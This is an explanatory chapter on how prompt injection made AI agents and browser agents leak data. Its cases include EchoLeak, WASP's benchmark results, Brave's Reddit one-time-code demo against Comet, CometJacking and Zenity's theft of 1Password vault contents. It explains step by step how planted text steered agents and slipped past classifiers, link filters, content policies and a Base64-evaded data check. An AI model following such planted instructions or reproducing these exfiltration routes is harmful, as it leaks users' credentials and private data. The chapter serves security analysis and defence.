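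Link previews can leak data without anyone clicking a link. When someone posts an address in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app fetches the page to show its title and a picture. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, explains that a chatbot under an attacker's influence could post an address containing private data, and the app would send that data to the attacker's server when it fetched the preview.

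A content security policy on the chatbot maker's website does not help here, because the reply appears in someone else's app. That app's preview service can make the request from its own server, without involving the user's browser. Whoever connects a chatbot to the app has to switch previews off, which Slack lets a program do for each message it posts. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can operate through messaging apps, was exposed by default on Telegram, where a single setting prevents the leak.

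An email can leak data just as a preview can. In May 2026, Willison reported on Microsoft Copilot Cowork, an agent that could send messages to its user's own inbox without asking for approval. The inbox displayed outside images, so opening such a message sent data to the attacker. That data could include links for downloading the user's files without a sign-in, which made each link a credential for its file.

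### EchoLeak

In the Bing Chat demonstration, the victim had to visit a page with planted text and chat about it. EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, let the attacker start by sending an email. Researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, built a working version in January 2025. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives their account of it.

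When an employee asks Copilot a question, the software first searches the employee's mailbox, files and Teams chats for relevant material and gives it to the model. The attacker's email therefore had to turn up in that search. Aim Labs wrote a long email with separate parts on common office subjects, such as staff leave, so that searches on many topics would return some part of it. The employee did not have to open the email. Once Copilot had retrieved it, the email's instructions led the model to choose the most sensitive item in its input and write an image address containing it.

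Microsoft had several defences against this, and Aim Labs found a way past each one.

| Defence | How the attack got past it |
|---|---|
| A classifier that looked for instructions aimed at Copilot in incoming text | The email read as if its instructions were for the human recipient and did not mention AI |
| A filter that removed outside links and images from replies | The filter recognised one way of writing them in Markdown but missed another |
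| A content security policy that limited images to approved sites | A Microsoft Teams service on the list would fetch any address that someone gave it |
| References that showed which documents a reply drew on | The email included a request not to mention it, and Copilot complied |

The leak was automatic mainly because of the Teams service. The employee's browser requested an image from the service, which the policy allowed, and the request included the attacker's address with the secret in it. A Microsoft server then requested that address. A content security policy restricts the browser's requests, including those that follow a redirect, but not requests between servers. An earlier version of the attack used SharePoint in the same way, but the victim first had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site.

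EchoLeak involves two confused deputies in Hardy's sense, since Copilot read the files for the attacker and Teams sent the request.

Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, report that Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025 and that the flaw was disclosed on 11 June, with no evidence that anyone had used the attack on customers. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026), Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

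Reddy and Gujral also call EchoLeak the first known case in which prompt injection caused concrete data exfiltration from an AI system in production. But Rehberger had taken data from Bing Chat, a public product, two years earlier, also without a click. Ravia claims more narrowly that earlier attacks either required the user to direct the chatbot to a malicious source or tightly restricted what the attacker could take. "Zero-click" is also slightly misleading, because the employee still has to ask Copilot something, though a routine question is enough.

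### No rule for opening a page

A browser agent can leak the same data by opening the attacker's address as a page, and content security policy does not prevent that. W3C's 2026 draft has two directives for navigation, the move from one page to another. `form-action` limits where a page's forms may send their contents, and `frame-ancestors` limits which sites may embed the page. Neither restricts following a link or opening a new address. With only the image rule above, Ana's browser would refuse to load a picture from notes.example but would open notes.example as a page.

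Browser developers knew about this gap and tried to close it. Paicu (2018), in *Intent to implement and ship*, proposed adding a `navigate-to` directive to Chrome. It would have let a site list the addresses its pages could send a visitor to, whether through a link, a form or a script. Google's advertising teams were interested because they wanted to ensure that an advertisement led to the page the advertiser had declared. The directive was still in W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2021).

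`navigate-to` could also have stopped some theft. *AutoNav* (Eriksson and Sabelfeld, 2020) describes an injected script that reads a session cookie and then sends the browser to the attacker's site with the cookie in the query string. `navigate-to` could block that last step, which the policies then in use could not.

But Eriksson and Sabelfeld also found that the directive created new leaks, including for sites that did not use it. Many sites redirect visitors who are not signed in to a login page. An attacker's page could set a policy that allowed a site's private page but not its login page, then send the visitor to the private page. If the browser blocked the redirect to the login page, the attacker learned that the visitor was not signed in. The same-origin policy normally keeps one site from learning whether a visitor is signed in to another.

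The directive never shipped in any browser, according to Mozilla's *Remove (disabled by default) CSP directive `navigate-to`*, and W3C's editors removed it from the draft in September 2022. Mozilla cites concerns about leaks of this kind. WebKit (2022), the project behind Safari's browser engine, notes that few browser makers had supported it beyond Chrome's experimental version. Chrome's developers later deleted their code for it too, according to Mozilla's *[wpt-sync] Sync PR 48118*.

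Even a working `navigate-to` would probably have done little to restrict a browser agent. Eriksson and Sabelfeld's list of what it covered does not include addresses typed by the user, because the directive restricted pages rather than users. An agent that opens an address through the browser's own controls is doing much the same thing as typing it. W3C also specifies that policies should not interfere with browser extensions, and some browser agents are extensions.

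Protection also depends on who writes the policy. Microsoft could protect Bing Chat's users because it controlled the page where the replies appeared. The maker of an AI browser can likewise write a policy that blocks the image leak in the panel that displays the agent's replies. But the agent also works on pages that belong to other people, and an attacker will not write a policy that stops the agent from leaving the attacker's page. Ana's email provider could write a strict policy for her mailbox, but it would not apply to an address that the agent opens in a new tab. A limit on those addresses has to come from the browser or from the software that carries out the model's actions.

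## 2025: agents begin to work in the user's own signed-in browser

An agent that opens an attacker's address can leak only what it can read, and at the start of 2025 some agents could read very little. OpenAI's Operator, released in January, controlled a browser on OpenAI's computers. That browser had none of the user's cookies, so Operator could read Ana's mailbox only if she signed in to it there.

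Developers then put agents into the browser that people already use. Perplexity released Comet on 9 July 2025, according to the *Comet* entry in the AI Agent Index, an MIT-hosted catalogue of agents. An agent in Comet starts with access to every account the user is signed in to. Ana might ask it only to compare kettle prices, but her mailbox, her bank and cloud.example would all accept its requests as hers.

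This is convenient because Ana doesn't have to sign in again for each task. But when the agent worked in a remote browser, she chose which accounts it could use by signing in to them, and she no longer makes that choice when it works in her own browser.

### What each design can reach

*Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) classifies agents by where their browser runs and what it keeps. The table follows this classification and adds agents built into a browser.

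| Design | Example | Accounts the agent can open | Files on the user's computer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Remote browser that keeps nothing | OpenOperator | None of the user's | None |
| Remote browser that can keep sign-ins | OpenAI Operator | Those the user has signed in to there | None |
| Fresh browser on the user's computer | Browser Use | Those it signs in to during the task | Yes |
| Extension in the user's browser | Do Browser | Every account open in the browser | If the user allows it |
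| Agent built into the browser | Comet | Every account open in the browser, and services connected to the assistant | Depends on the product |

A remote browser protects accounts only as long as the user stays signed out of them. Operator could preserve sign-ins between sessions, so if Ana signed in to an account there on Monday, she might still be signed in on Friday, when the agent read a planted comment. A fresh browser on her own computer lacks her cookies, but it can open local files, where developers often keep SSH keys and API keys.

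An extension and a built-in agent have much the same access to accounts. Both can also reach saved passwords, because the browser fills them into login forms. A built-in agent may have more tools. The security company Trail of Bits examined Comet before its release and found that the assistant could fetch pages, control the browser and search the browsing history. These tools moved data between the user's computer, which held the cookies, and Perplexity's servers, which ran the assistant.

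The AI Agent Index found no sandbox to limit what Comet's agent could reach, and its reviewers never saw the agent stop to ask for approval. The user could stop the agent at any time, but had to be watching its list of actions to notice a problem.

In November 2025, a dispute arose over how far a built-in agent can reach beyond the browser. The index mentions reports of a hidden interface in Comet that could run commands on the computer itself. The security company SquareX demonstrated an attack that used this interface through a malicious extension impersonating one of Comet's own. Perplexity told SecurityWeek that this was "fake security research", because someone would have to persuade the user to load malware by hand, but it added protections anyway. The objection to the attack is fair, but it doesn't settle whether a browser should contain such an interface.

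### WASP: starting an attack and completing it

For an attack to succeed, the agent must have access and also follow the planted text through several steps. *WASP* (Evtimov, Zharmagambetov and colleagues, 2025) measured how often agents did so. The tests ran on closed servers, using working copies of GitLab, where programmers store code and discuss faults in it, and of a forum modelled on Reddit. The attacker had an ordinary account and could only file an issue or write a post or comment. The user asked the agent to do something small, such as give an issue a thumbs-up.

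One of the benchmark's 21 attacker goals is almost exactly the leak described at the beginning. The agent has to create a new access token for the user's GitLab account, which works much like an API key, place it in a web address on the attacker's server and open that address. The page does not need to display any secret beforehand, because the agent creates one. The user has no reason to revoke a token they don't know about.

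Another goal is to do the same with a deploy token, which gives access to a project's code. Three more are to send out other data in a web address, such as the title of the user's latest private message. The remaining goals include deleting a project and posting insults.

Evtimov and colleagues measured how often attacks started and how often they succeeded. A second model read the agent's reasoning and actions to judge whether it had started pursuing the attacker's goal. To measure success, a program checked the state of the websites afterwards or whether the data had reached the attacker's server. The table gives results from 84 test cases for agents without an extra warning in their instructions.

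| Model running the agent | Attack started | Attack completed |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, reading page text | 32% | 1% |
| GPT-4o, reading page text and labelled screenshots | 43% | 4% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5 | 58% | 6% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.7 | 54% | 4% |
| OpenAI o1 | 86% | 17% |

OpenAI had trained o1 to give text from tools, including web pages, less authority than the user's request, but the model still began pursuing the attacker's goal in 72 of the 84 cases and completed it in 14. A warning about planted instructions halved the rate at which GPT-4o began pursuing the attacker's goal when it read only page text, but reduced Claude Sonnet 3.7's rate only from 54% to 50%.

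Most of the attacks that agents began to carry out failed because the agents were poor at using websites. In one run, GPT-4o opened the user's account settings as the planted text required, then went back to the original task and could no longer find the issue it was supposed to comment on. Evtimov and colleagues call this "security by incompetence". This protection is weak because every improvement in the agent's ordinary work also makes it better at finishing an attack.

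Later experiments support that explanation. *WebTrap* (Liu, Pan and colleagues, 2026) reused WASP's goals but simplified the controls, so that an agent would not seem safe merely because it couldn't operate them. In the longest GitLab tasks, the agent completed one of WASP's original plain-text attacks in 58% of cases. *WebTrap*'s own attack, which spread the instructions over several pages, succeeded in 67%. The agent often then finished the user's task as well, which would leave the user with little reason to suspect anything. *WebTrap* used a newer model, so the simpler controls may not account for the whole difference from WASP.

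WASP's low completion rates also reflect the attacks it used. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (2026) found that an agent could finish one of the user's tasks without reading the issue description that contained the planted text. It replaced that task with one that required reading the description, and it gave the issues less conspicuous titles. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) adds that an agent may appear to resist an attack only because carrying it out takes too much work.

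Automated attacks can succeed much more often than fixed ones. *MUZZLE* (2026) describes a system that searches for attacks by itself. It completed its attacks in 86.7% of runs, compared with 20% for WASP's fixed text, but the test environments differed, so the comparison is imprecise.

WASP therefore showed that planted text could divert an agent on an ordinary website, but its completion rates are closer to a minimum than to a forecast. These rates also combine all 21 goals, so they do not measure how often an agent would send out the access token.

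### "Mind the Web": what four agents gave away

In a June 2025 paper, Shapira and colleagues tested products instead of research agents. They built a harmless-looking travel site called City-Explorer and planted instructions in its visitors' comments, as text or images. They then gave each agent an ordinary task, such as summarising the page. The comments presented the attacker's goal as helpful to the task, so following them did not obviously conflict with the user's request.

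What each agent gave away depended largely on what it could reach:

- **Do Browser**, the extension, opened a Facebook login form, uncovered the password that the browser had filled in and sent it to the attacker's server. In other demonstrations it joined a video call with the user's camera and microphone on, and posted a false confession of theft on Twitter.
- **Browser Use**, which ran a fresh browser on the user's computer, opened a local file and submitted its contents to the attacker's site. The file was the computer's hosts file, a list of network names that is rarely secret, but an SSH key is also a file.
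- **OpenOperator**, in a remote browser with no stored sign-ins, reloaded a page until it crashed.
- **OpenAI Operator** left City-Explorer for a news site that the planted text recommended. In another test it gave the user a false summary. It also posted an embarrassing comment under the user's name, on a site where the user was signed in.

Neither remote agent leaked a credential in these demonstrations. This is some evidence for keeping an agent in a separate browser, but it doesn't show that the agent is safe there. Shapira and colleagues list Operator's design among those exposed to credential theft once the user signs in to an account through Operator.

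Operator could also detect some planted instructions, and it normally asked before submitting a comment. It posted the embarrassing comment when the user had asked it to handle the whole task alone while they went for coffee. The researchers found it much harder to make Operator post anything unasked when the user had not made such a request.

The paper reports success rates of 80% to 100%, far above WASP's, in further tests of Browser Use on different models. Each combination of model and attack had 20 trials. The researchers sometimes reworded an attack that failed at first, so the rates include attacks adjusted to their target. They do not include the theft of the Facebook password, which was a demonstration on a different agent.

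When Shapira and colleagues reported the flaws, Browser Use's developers replied that protection required several layers, such as lists of permitted sites and accounts with limited privileges.

### Comet before its release

Perplexity had evidence of the problem in Comet before releasing it. In April 2025 it hired Trail of Bits to attack the browser, and the firm's *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) describes the results. The testers built five working attacks. In each, the user asked for a summary of a page that the attacker controlled, and the user's Gmail messages ended up on the attacker's server.

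One of the attacks leaked the user's emails through a web address that the agent opened. The attacker's page presented an article as split into pieces that the agent had to collect from separate addresses. One of those addresses redirected the browser to Gmail, which accepted the session cookie and displayed the inbox. The agent treated the inbox as a piece of the article, then opened an address that was supposed to join the pieces, with the text of the emails in the query string.

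In this attack, a redirect from the attacker's site opened Gmail without the agent requesting it. A check on the address that the agent requested would have covered only the attacker's site. To detect the redirect, the software had to check the address where the browser arrived.

The model recognised some attacks, but not reliably. One attack worked only because the testers had made spelling mistakes in the planted text. When they corrected the mistakes, the agent identified the text as fraudulent and ignored it.

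Perplexity's security lead, Kyle Polley, said the audit had helped the company find and close these gaps before launch. Comet came out in July, and within three weeks another company had found a way to do something similar.

### Brave's Reddit demonstration

Brave, which makes a competing browser, was developing an agent of its own and looked at how others had built theirs. Chaikin and Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, published Brave's findings on Comet in August 2025. In their demonstration, a user opens a Reddit post and clicks Comet's button for summarising the page. One of the comments contains planted text, hidden behind the grey box that Reddit uses to cover spoilers. The agent reads it, and the rest happens without any further action by the user:

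1. The agent opens the user's account page at Perplexity and reads the email address there.
2. It opens Perplexity's login page under a slightly different host name. The browser treats this as another site, so the user's existing login does not apply. The agent enters the email address, and Perplexity emails a one-time code.
3. It opens Gmail, where the user is signed in, and reads the code.
4. It replies to the planted comment on Reddit with the email address and the code.

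The attacker reads the reply and signs in to the user's Perplexity account.

Every site involved worked as intended. Reddit showed a comment, Gmail showed an email to the account's owner, and Perplexity sent a code to the right mailbox. An emailed code is meant to prove that the person signing in controls the mailbox, but the agent could open it too. Chaikin and Sahib trace the fault to Comet, which passed part of the page to the model without separating it from the user's request.

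The agent leaked the credentials by posting them in a Reddit comment, so it did not need to contact the attacker's server. A list of permitted sites that included Reddit, the site the user had asked about, would not have stopped the leak. The method has drawbacks for an attacker because the code expires quickly, anyone else reading the thread could use it first, and the user could find the reply under their own name. Because posting is a separate action, a browser can ask the user to approve it first. Chaikin and Sahib recommend such confirmation for sensitive actions, and suggest that a request to summarise a Reddit discussion should not give an agent access to email.

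Brave reported the flaw to Perplexity on 25 July, and Perplexity made a first fix two days later. Brave tested the fix on 28 July and found it incomplete. The attack appeared to be blocked on 13 August, and Brave published its account a week later. Brave then tested once more, found that Perplexity still had not fully stopped this kind of attack, and reported it again.

Perplexity's head of communications said that the vulnerability "is fixed" and that the company had worked directly with Brave to fix it, according to PPC Land's *Comet browser faces multiple security vulnerabilities from prompt injection*. That may be true of the attack Brave first demonstrated, but Brave's later update concerns the wider kind of attack, which a fix for one example may not prevent.

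Willison (2025), in a note also titled *Agentic Browser Security*, was sceptical of Brave's advice to separate the user's instructions from the page, because nobody had yet shown a convincing way for a model to tell the two apart. Willison strongly expected that an agentic browser extension could not be built safely, which would apply to Brave's planned agent as much as to Comet.

### October: the data leaves in an address

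Brave's next demonstrations were attacks on Comet and on Fellou, another AI browser, which Chaikin and Sahib published in *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots* on 21 October 2025. These attacks no longer needed a public comment, because in both the agent sent the data by opening a web address.

The Comet attack used a feature that lets users take a screenshot of a page and ask about it. The attacker had written instructions in faint blue on a yellow background, which a person would hardly notice. Comet extracted the text from the screenshot and passed it to the model with the user's question. A filter that removed hidden text from the page's code would have missed these instructions, because they were part of an image.

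Fellou resisted some hidden instructions but followed visible ones. It sent a page's content to its model as soon as the user asked it to visit the page, so the user did not even have to request a summary.

According to Willison's notes, also titled *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, Comet's agent then opened the user's Perplexity account page, read the email address and sent it to an outside server by opening a URL that contained it. Fellou's agent opened Gmail, read the subject line of the most recent email and sent it out in a query string. Email addresses and most subject lines are not credentials, but some services put one-time codes in subject lines, and an attacker who had just requested a code could receive it this way.

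This method needs fewer permissions than the Reddit attack and leaves less for the user to find. The agent does not post anything, so a browser that asks for approval only before posting or sending would let the request through. In the 1Password case a few months later, the agent opened an address that contained the contents of a password vault.

Brave had reported the Fellou flaw on 20 August and the Comet flaw on 1 October. Its article does not mention a fix for either, and Willison could not tell whether the companies had made one.

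Brave's *Prompt injection flaw in Opera Neon* describes a third case, in which an attack made Opera's AI browser read the email address on the user's Opera account page and send it to the attacker's server. The instructions were in hidden parts of a web page's code. Opera closed the report as "Not Applicable" three days after receiving it, then contacted Brave again on 20 October. Brave published the details only after checking that Opera's fix worked. The browser was still in early access, so few people had been exposed.

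### CometJacking: the instruction arrives in the link

The attacks above all begin with text on a page. In CometJacking, which LayerX published in October 2025, the instruction is in the link itself. A Perplexity web address can contain a question, and opening the address starts a conversation with the assistant. This is useful for sharing a search, but it also lets an attacker write the question. When the user clicks the attacker's link, Comet reads the question from the query string and treats it as the user's own.

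LayerX's link made the assistant search its memory and connected services instead of the web. The memory holds material from the user's earlier requests, such as an email the assistant helped write. The services were Gmail and Google Calendar, which a user can connect to Perplexity. LayerX reports that one test link took the user's emails and another took calendar invitations.

Perplexity had a check meant to stop sensitive data from leaving. LayerX got past it by having the assistant first convert the data to Base64, which represents any data using a set of 64 characters. Like percent-encoding, Base64 needs no key, and anyone can reverse it. The check evidently detected sensitive data only in its ordinary form.

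The assistant ran a short program that sent the stolen data in the body of a POST request, rather than in the address of a page it opened. The query string was used here to deliver the instruction to the assistant. A limit on the pages the agent may open would not necessarily cover a program that the assistant runs, especially if the program runs on the company's servers.

CometJacking resembles cross-site request forgery, but the attacker also obtains data, because Comet's assistant reads it and sends it to the attacker. The attack bypasses any defence that marks web pages as untrusted, because the instruction arrives as if it were the user's question. LayerX says that the assistant's memory can contain credentials, but LayerX's published tests took emails and calendar data.

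LayerX reported the flaw to Perplexity on 27 August 2025. By LayerX's account, Perplexity replied that it could not identify any security impact and marked the report "Not Applicable", the label Opera later used for Brave's report. After publication, a Perplexity spokesperson said that the report had been poorly worded and that LayerX had not answered requests for clarification, according to *Why AI Browsers Like Perplexity's Comet Could Make the Web Riskier* (Perrigo, 2025). The spokesperson added that Perplexity had later found the problem independently and patched it, and that nobody had exploited it. The patch makes Perplexity's first assessment hard to defend.

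Perplexity had just made Comet free, after offering it only to paying subscribers. OpenAI released ChatGPT Atlas later in October, and its chief information security officer, Dane Stuckey, published a statement about prompt injection and the browser's protections. In *Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT Atlas*, Willison (2025) expected the next few months to show how well those protections worked.

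On 31 October, Amazon (2025) cited CometJacking in a letter demanding changes from Perplexity. Amazon was not a neutral judge of the risk, because it had a commercial dispute with Perplexity over Comet's shopping in its store. But its complaint included a practical security point: Comet did not identify itself as an agent, which made it harder for Amazon to tell the agent's visits from the customer's own.

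## November 2025 to February 2026: a password vault is read and its contents sent by opening a page

The attacks on Comet in 2025 took emails, calendar entries and a one-time code. A password manager holds far more because it stores the logins for people's other accounts. In November 2025, Zenity Labs, the research group of Zenity, which sells security software for AI agents, reported an attack on 1Password users through Comet. A calendar invitation led the agent to open the user's vault, read a username and password, and send both to an attacker by opening a web address. In a second version, the attacker took over the whole 1Password account.

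Two months earlier, 1Password and Perplexity had announced a partnership that brought 1Password's browser extension to Comet. The extension fills in saved logins on the sites they belong to, and CyberInsider reported at the launch that it would do so while keeping sensitive data out of the AI's processing context. That promise applied only when the extension filled in logins, and Zenity Labs got around it by steering the agent to 1Password's own website, which displays the same passwords for people to read.

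### How the vault came to be open

1Password protects an account with two secrets. The user chooses the account password, and the user's device generates a Secret Key, a code that nobody could guess and 1Password cannot recover. Signing in on a new device requires both, so a criminal who steals only the account password can't open the vault from another computer.

Neither secret protects the vault once it is unlocked. In the setup Zenity Labs tested, the extension stayed unlocked for up to eight hours by default.

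The unlocked extension also signed the browser in to 1Password.com, where users can view and edit their vaults. This automatic sign-in dates from 2024. In *Not seeing the "automatic 1P website login" indicated in latest BLOG post*, a customer, mtoboll (2024), described entering an email address, the Secret Key, the password and a second factor on the first visit, after which the extension signed in automatically. According to 1Password, the sign-in page requests login details from the extension, which responds only to pages at certain 1Password addresses. This keeps other websites from obtaining the details. But the address is the same whether the user or an agent opens the page, so the extension signed the agent in just as it would have signed in the user.

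The attack also worked only if the user asked Comet to handle the invitation. The top of the invitation showed ordinary meeting details. The planted text was further down, where the user was unlikely to look, and presented the steps of the theft as part of handling the meeting. Zenity Labs chose a calendar invitation because people often let assistants manage their calendars, but notes that an email, a document or a web page could carry the same text.

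Zenity Labs calls this a zero-click attack. As with EchoLeak, the user doesn't have to click on anything from the attacker but does have to ask the AI for help. Zenity Labs published a video showing that Comet could carry out the attack, but did not report how often it succeeded.

### From the invitation to the attacker's address

The agent worked in Comet's side panel while the calendar stayed on the screen. The table lists each action, the permission that allowed it and the check that might have stopped it.

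| What the agent did | Permission it used | Missing check |
|---|---|---|
| Read the invitation | The user's request and logged-in session at the calendar | Nothing reliably separated the organiser's text from the user's request |
| Went to 1Password.com | Comet's freedom to open websites | No rule kept a calendar task away from the vault |
| Entered the vault | The unlocked extension and automatic sign-in | The extension did not ask whether the user wanted to sign in |
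| Searched for a login and opened it | The new session at 1Password.com | The site did not ask for the account password again |
| Revealed the password and read it | The button that shows a hidden password | No prompt asked the user to approve |
| Opened the attacker's address, with the username and password in it | Ordinary navigation | Nothing checked the destination or the contents |
| Went back to the calendar and reported success | The side panel | The report to the user left out the vault |

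Once the agent had revealed the password, the password was text in the model's input, and only a limit on the addresses the agent could open would have stopped it from sending the password out. The final request had the same form as the one that carried Ana's password to notes.example.

Zenity Labs' *Perplexity Comet* describes code in Comet that checks an address before the agent opens it. The code stops the agent from opening the browser's internal pages, including its settings and built-in password manager, as well as files on the user's computer, certain types of document, addresses on a list that Perplexity controls, and sites the user has blocked. The agent therefore cannot open the page where the browser keeps saved passwords. A 1Password vault may hold the same passwords, but the rule for internal pages does not cover it because it is on an ordinary website.

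### From one password to the whole account

Zenity Labs extended the attack to take over the 1Password account. The agent opened the account settings and started to change the password. The change required the current password, a common precaution against someone using an unlocked computer, but the extension filled it in. The agent then set a new password the attacker had chosen.

After a password change, 1Password offers the user a new Emergency Kit, a document for recovering access to the account. The agent took the email address and Secret Key from it and sent them to the attacker by opening another web address. The attacker now had everything 1Password normally requires to sign in on a new computer.

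Multi-factor sign-in would have stopped the takeover at its last step, because the attacker did not have the second factor. But the attacker can steal vault entries without signing in to 1Password, then use each password at the site it belongs to.

That site may also ask for a second factor. But 1Password can store and fill one-time codes, and if a user keeps them there, an agent that can open the entry could presumably read the current code along with the password. The attacker would have to use the code almost immediately. Zenity Labs demonstrated only the theft of a username and password.

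Companies can block the takeover in two other ways, though neither hides the vault's entries. Zenity Labs says that employees who open 1Password through single sign-on, a company login that covers many services, cannot reset their own 1Password password without an administrator's approval. Administrators can also use 1Password's team policies to prevent employees from downloading an Emergency Kit. This would probably have removed the agent's source for the Secret Key.

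In August 2026, *1Password in the browser 8.12.32* (1P_SimonH, 2026) announced that the extension would block attempts to paste the Secret Key into a website. This protects a user who has landed on a fake login page, but it would probably not stop an agent that reads the key and writes it directly into a web address.

The user would be more likely to notice the takeover than the leak of a single entry, which leaves the vault looking the same as before. After a takeover, the old password stops working, and the user will find out the next time they have to type it.

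### Whose flaw it was

Zenity Labs told both companies about the attack on the same day and published it four months later.

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 3 November 2025 | Zenity Labs reports the attack to Perplexity and 1Password |
| 4 November | 1Password acknowledges the report and starts to investigate |
| 24 November | 1Password concludes that its product has no vulnerability, but says the report has contributed to planned changes |
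| 4 December | Perplexity acknowledges a vulnerability and says it is working on a fix |
| 17 December | Perplexity and Zenity Labs meet to discuss the fix |
| 30 January 2026 | 1Password publishes an advisory and marks the report as resolved |
| 13 February | Perplexity introduces its security measures |
| 3 March | Zenity makes the attack public |

In 1Password's *Security advisory for AI-assisted browsing interactions with the 1Password browser extension*, Hall and Sen (2026) call the problem an "ecosystem-level risk" that arises when an AI agent reads untrusted content and acts with a user's permissions. The agent did only what a signed-in user could have done, without breaking 1Password's encryption or bypassing any of its controls. The agent could not have used a locked extension.

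Hall and Sen correctly add that the extension gives access to one item at a time and has no command for exporting a whole vault. But the agent was on 1Password's website, where it could have opened one entry after another, and the takeover gave the attacker all of the entries.

Zenity (2026) states in its press release that 1Password confirmed the root cause lay in how Perplexity's browser carries out actions. 1Password's advisory is more guarded and names neither Perplexity nor Comet. Perplexity accepted that it had a vulnerability to fix.

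Zenity's co-founder and chief technology officer, Michael Bargury, called the problem "an inherent vulnerability in agentic systems," not a bug. A company can fix a bug once, but if a model can always mistake planted text for a request, someone has to limit what the agent can reach. Zenity Labs asked both companies to turn on their strongest limits by default. Zenity sells controls for AI agents, so it gains from this view, but the settings it recommended changing are free.

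Both companies contributed to the leak. Comet was the confused deputy because it let a stranger's text direct an agent that had the user's authority. But Hardy's remedy for the compiler was to change how the system granted permission, and 1Password granted it broadly, opening the vault for hours, without asking, to whatever was running in the browser. That was a reasonable convenience in 2024, when a visitor to 1Password.com was almost certainly a person. By September 2025, however, 1Password was promoting its extension for a browser with a built-in agent, so it had good reason to expect the agent to visit.

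### What the companies changed

Perplexity improved its detection of planted text, using this attack as an example. It also made the agent ask users to confirm sensitive actions more often, and let users and companies name sites where the agent cannot work.

Zenity Labs considers the last of these the strongest, because the software enforces it regardless of what the model has read. Listing 1Password would have prevented the entire attack. But users had to add it themselves, so anyone who didn't change the settings still depended on the detector and the prompts.

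Perplexity had treated a related attack more strictly. In October 2025, Zenity Labs reported that an invitation could make Comet open files on the user's computer and send out their contents. In one version, Comet warned the user only after it had sent the data. Perplexity rated the flaw critical and changed the browser's code to block the agent from accessing local files for all users. Zenity Labs confirmed on 13 February 2026 that the attack no longer worked.

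News coverage tended to treat the local-file and vault attacks as having the same outcome. CyberScoop's *Researchers discover suite of agentic AI browser vulnerabilities* described the flaws as patched in February 2026, and in its press release Zenity also credits Perplexity with addressing the underlying issue before publication. That is accurate for local files, but Zenity Labs is more cautious about the vault in its technical account, because the settings that would reliably have stopped the attack were optional.

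Perplexity could probably have blocked the agent from opening 1Password.com with little effort or disruption. The extension fills in logins on other websites, so the agent does not need to visit the vault to sign in to a shop. The code that Zenity Labs examined already checked a list of blocked addresses that Perplexity controlled. A default block would inconvenience the few people who want an agent to tidy their vault, but Perplexity could let them turn it off.

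1Password's main change was a setting to turn off automatic sign-in to its website. The company released the setting in December 2025, before publishing the advisory, and left automatic sign-in on by default. Zenity Labs also lists prompts before filling among the company's responses, but 1Password had introduced confirmation settings in August 2025 because of clickjacking, in which a web page tricks a person into clicking something they cannot see.

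In July 2026, 1Password went further and turned off automatic sign-in for all users. When a customer asked where the feature had gone (hegguardo, 2026, *'Unlock 1Password.com using the extension' function missing*), an employee replied that the company had disabled it temporarily while it completed other work. Support staff had told the customer that the company was adding safeguards and hoped to bring the feature back, but gave no date.

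Neither reply mentions AI agents, and 1Password had another reason to review the feature. The researcher Guy Fischman had found that the extension would send login details to any page on 1Password's domains, including some that included content from outside marketing platforms. An attacker would first have had to break into one of those platforms, which 1Password says did not happen. The company then restricted the feature to the pages that handle sign-in. It concluded that it should not have trusted every page it controlled to unlock a vault, which is close to Zenity Labs' complaint about trusting everything in the user's browser.

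### Keeping the vault locked

Without automatic sign-in, Comet's agent would have reached a login form. With the feature off, users have to type their account password to open the 1Password website, but people who mostly use the extension or the desktop app will seldom notice. As long as 1Password keeps the feature off for everyone, users don't have to find the setting themselves.

However, the user can still sign in by hand and leave the tab open. The agent could then use that session until the website locks itself, after a number of minutes set by the user. The extension might also fill in 1Password's own login form if the user has saved the account password in the vault. According to Zenity Labs, the attack would not have been possible if the user had both turned off automatic sign-in and turned on prompts before filling.

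Keeping the vault unlocked for a shorter period gives an attacker less time to read it. 1Password offers companies three presets for their employees. "Convenient" unlocks 1Password along with the computer, "Balanced" keeps it unlocked for up to eight hours on Mac and Windows, and "Strict" locks it whenever it is not in use. With "Strict", the user has to unlock 1Password for every login, which is tiresome without a fingerprint reader.

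Users can also set the extension to lock when the computer is idle, but the computer does not go idle if someone is working on it while the agent runs. Quitting the browser always locks the extension, but it also stops the agent.

Hall and Sen advise users to lock the extension when they browse untrusted content, but this advice is hard to follow when that content is an invitation in the user's own calendar.

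Confirmation before filling addresses a different weakness. 1Password fills in a login only after some input from the user, such as a click on a suggestion, and treats that input as a defence against fake websites, but an agent can supply the click. By default, the extension also submits the form after filling it in, so a single click can be enough to sign in.

With the setting "Ask before filling", the extension shows a prompt before it fills a form. Web pages cannot hide this prompt and, according to Zenity Labs, the agent cannot see it. In the takeover, the prompt would have appeared before the extension supplied the current account password, but not when the agent read an entry in the open vault, because showing a password on 1Password's website does not involve filling a form.

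As of December 2026, 1Password always asks before filling in a credit card, but users have to turn on prompts for logins. 1Password's *Manage autofill confirmation prompts* describes two drawbacks. The prompts add a step to every login, and some legitimate sites block pop-up alerts. On those sites the prompt never appears, and 1Password seems to have stopped working until the user fills in the form from the extension's menu. The protection also depends on the user reading each prompt, and Zenity Labs warns that people who see many prompts start to approve them by reflex.

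### Keeping the agent out of accounts

Blocking the agent from a site avoids those decisions. This works well for a password vault, because few tasks require the agent to open it. It works less well for a mailbox, which also holds credentials, because sorting email is among the main reasons people use an agent. Ana could block Comet from her vault and her bank without losing much, but if she also blocked it from her mailbox, it could no longer summarise her email.

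The user also has to think of every sensitive site in advance. This is easier for a company, which can make one list for all its employees, than for a person with a hundred accounts. When Zenity Labs published its findings in March 2026, Comet's default settings let the agent access the 1Password website.

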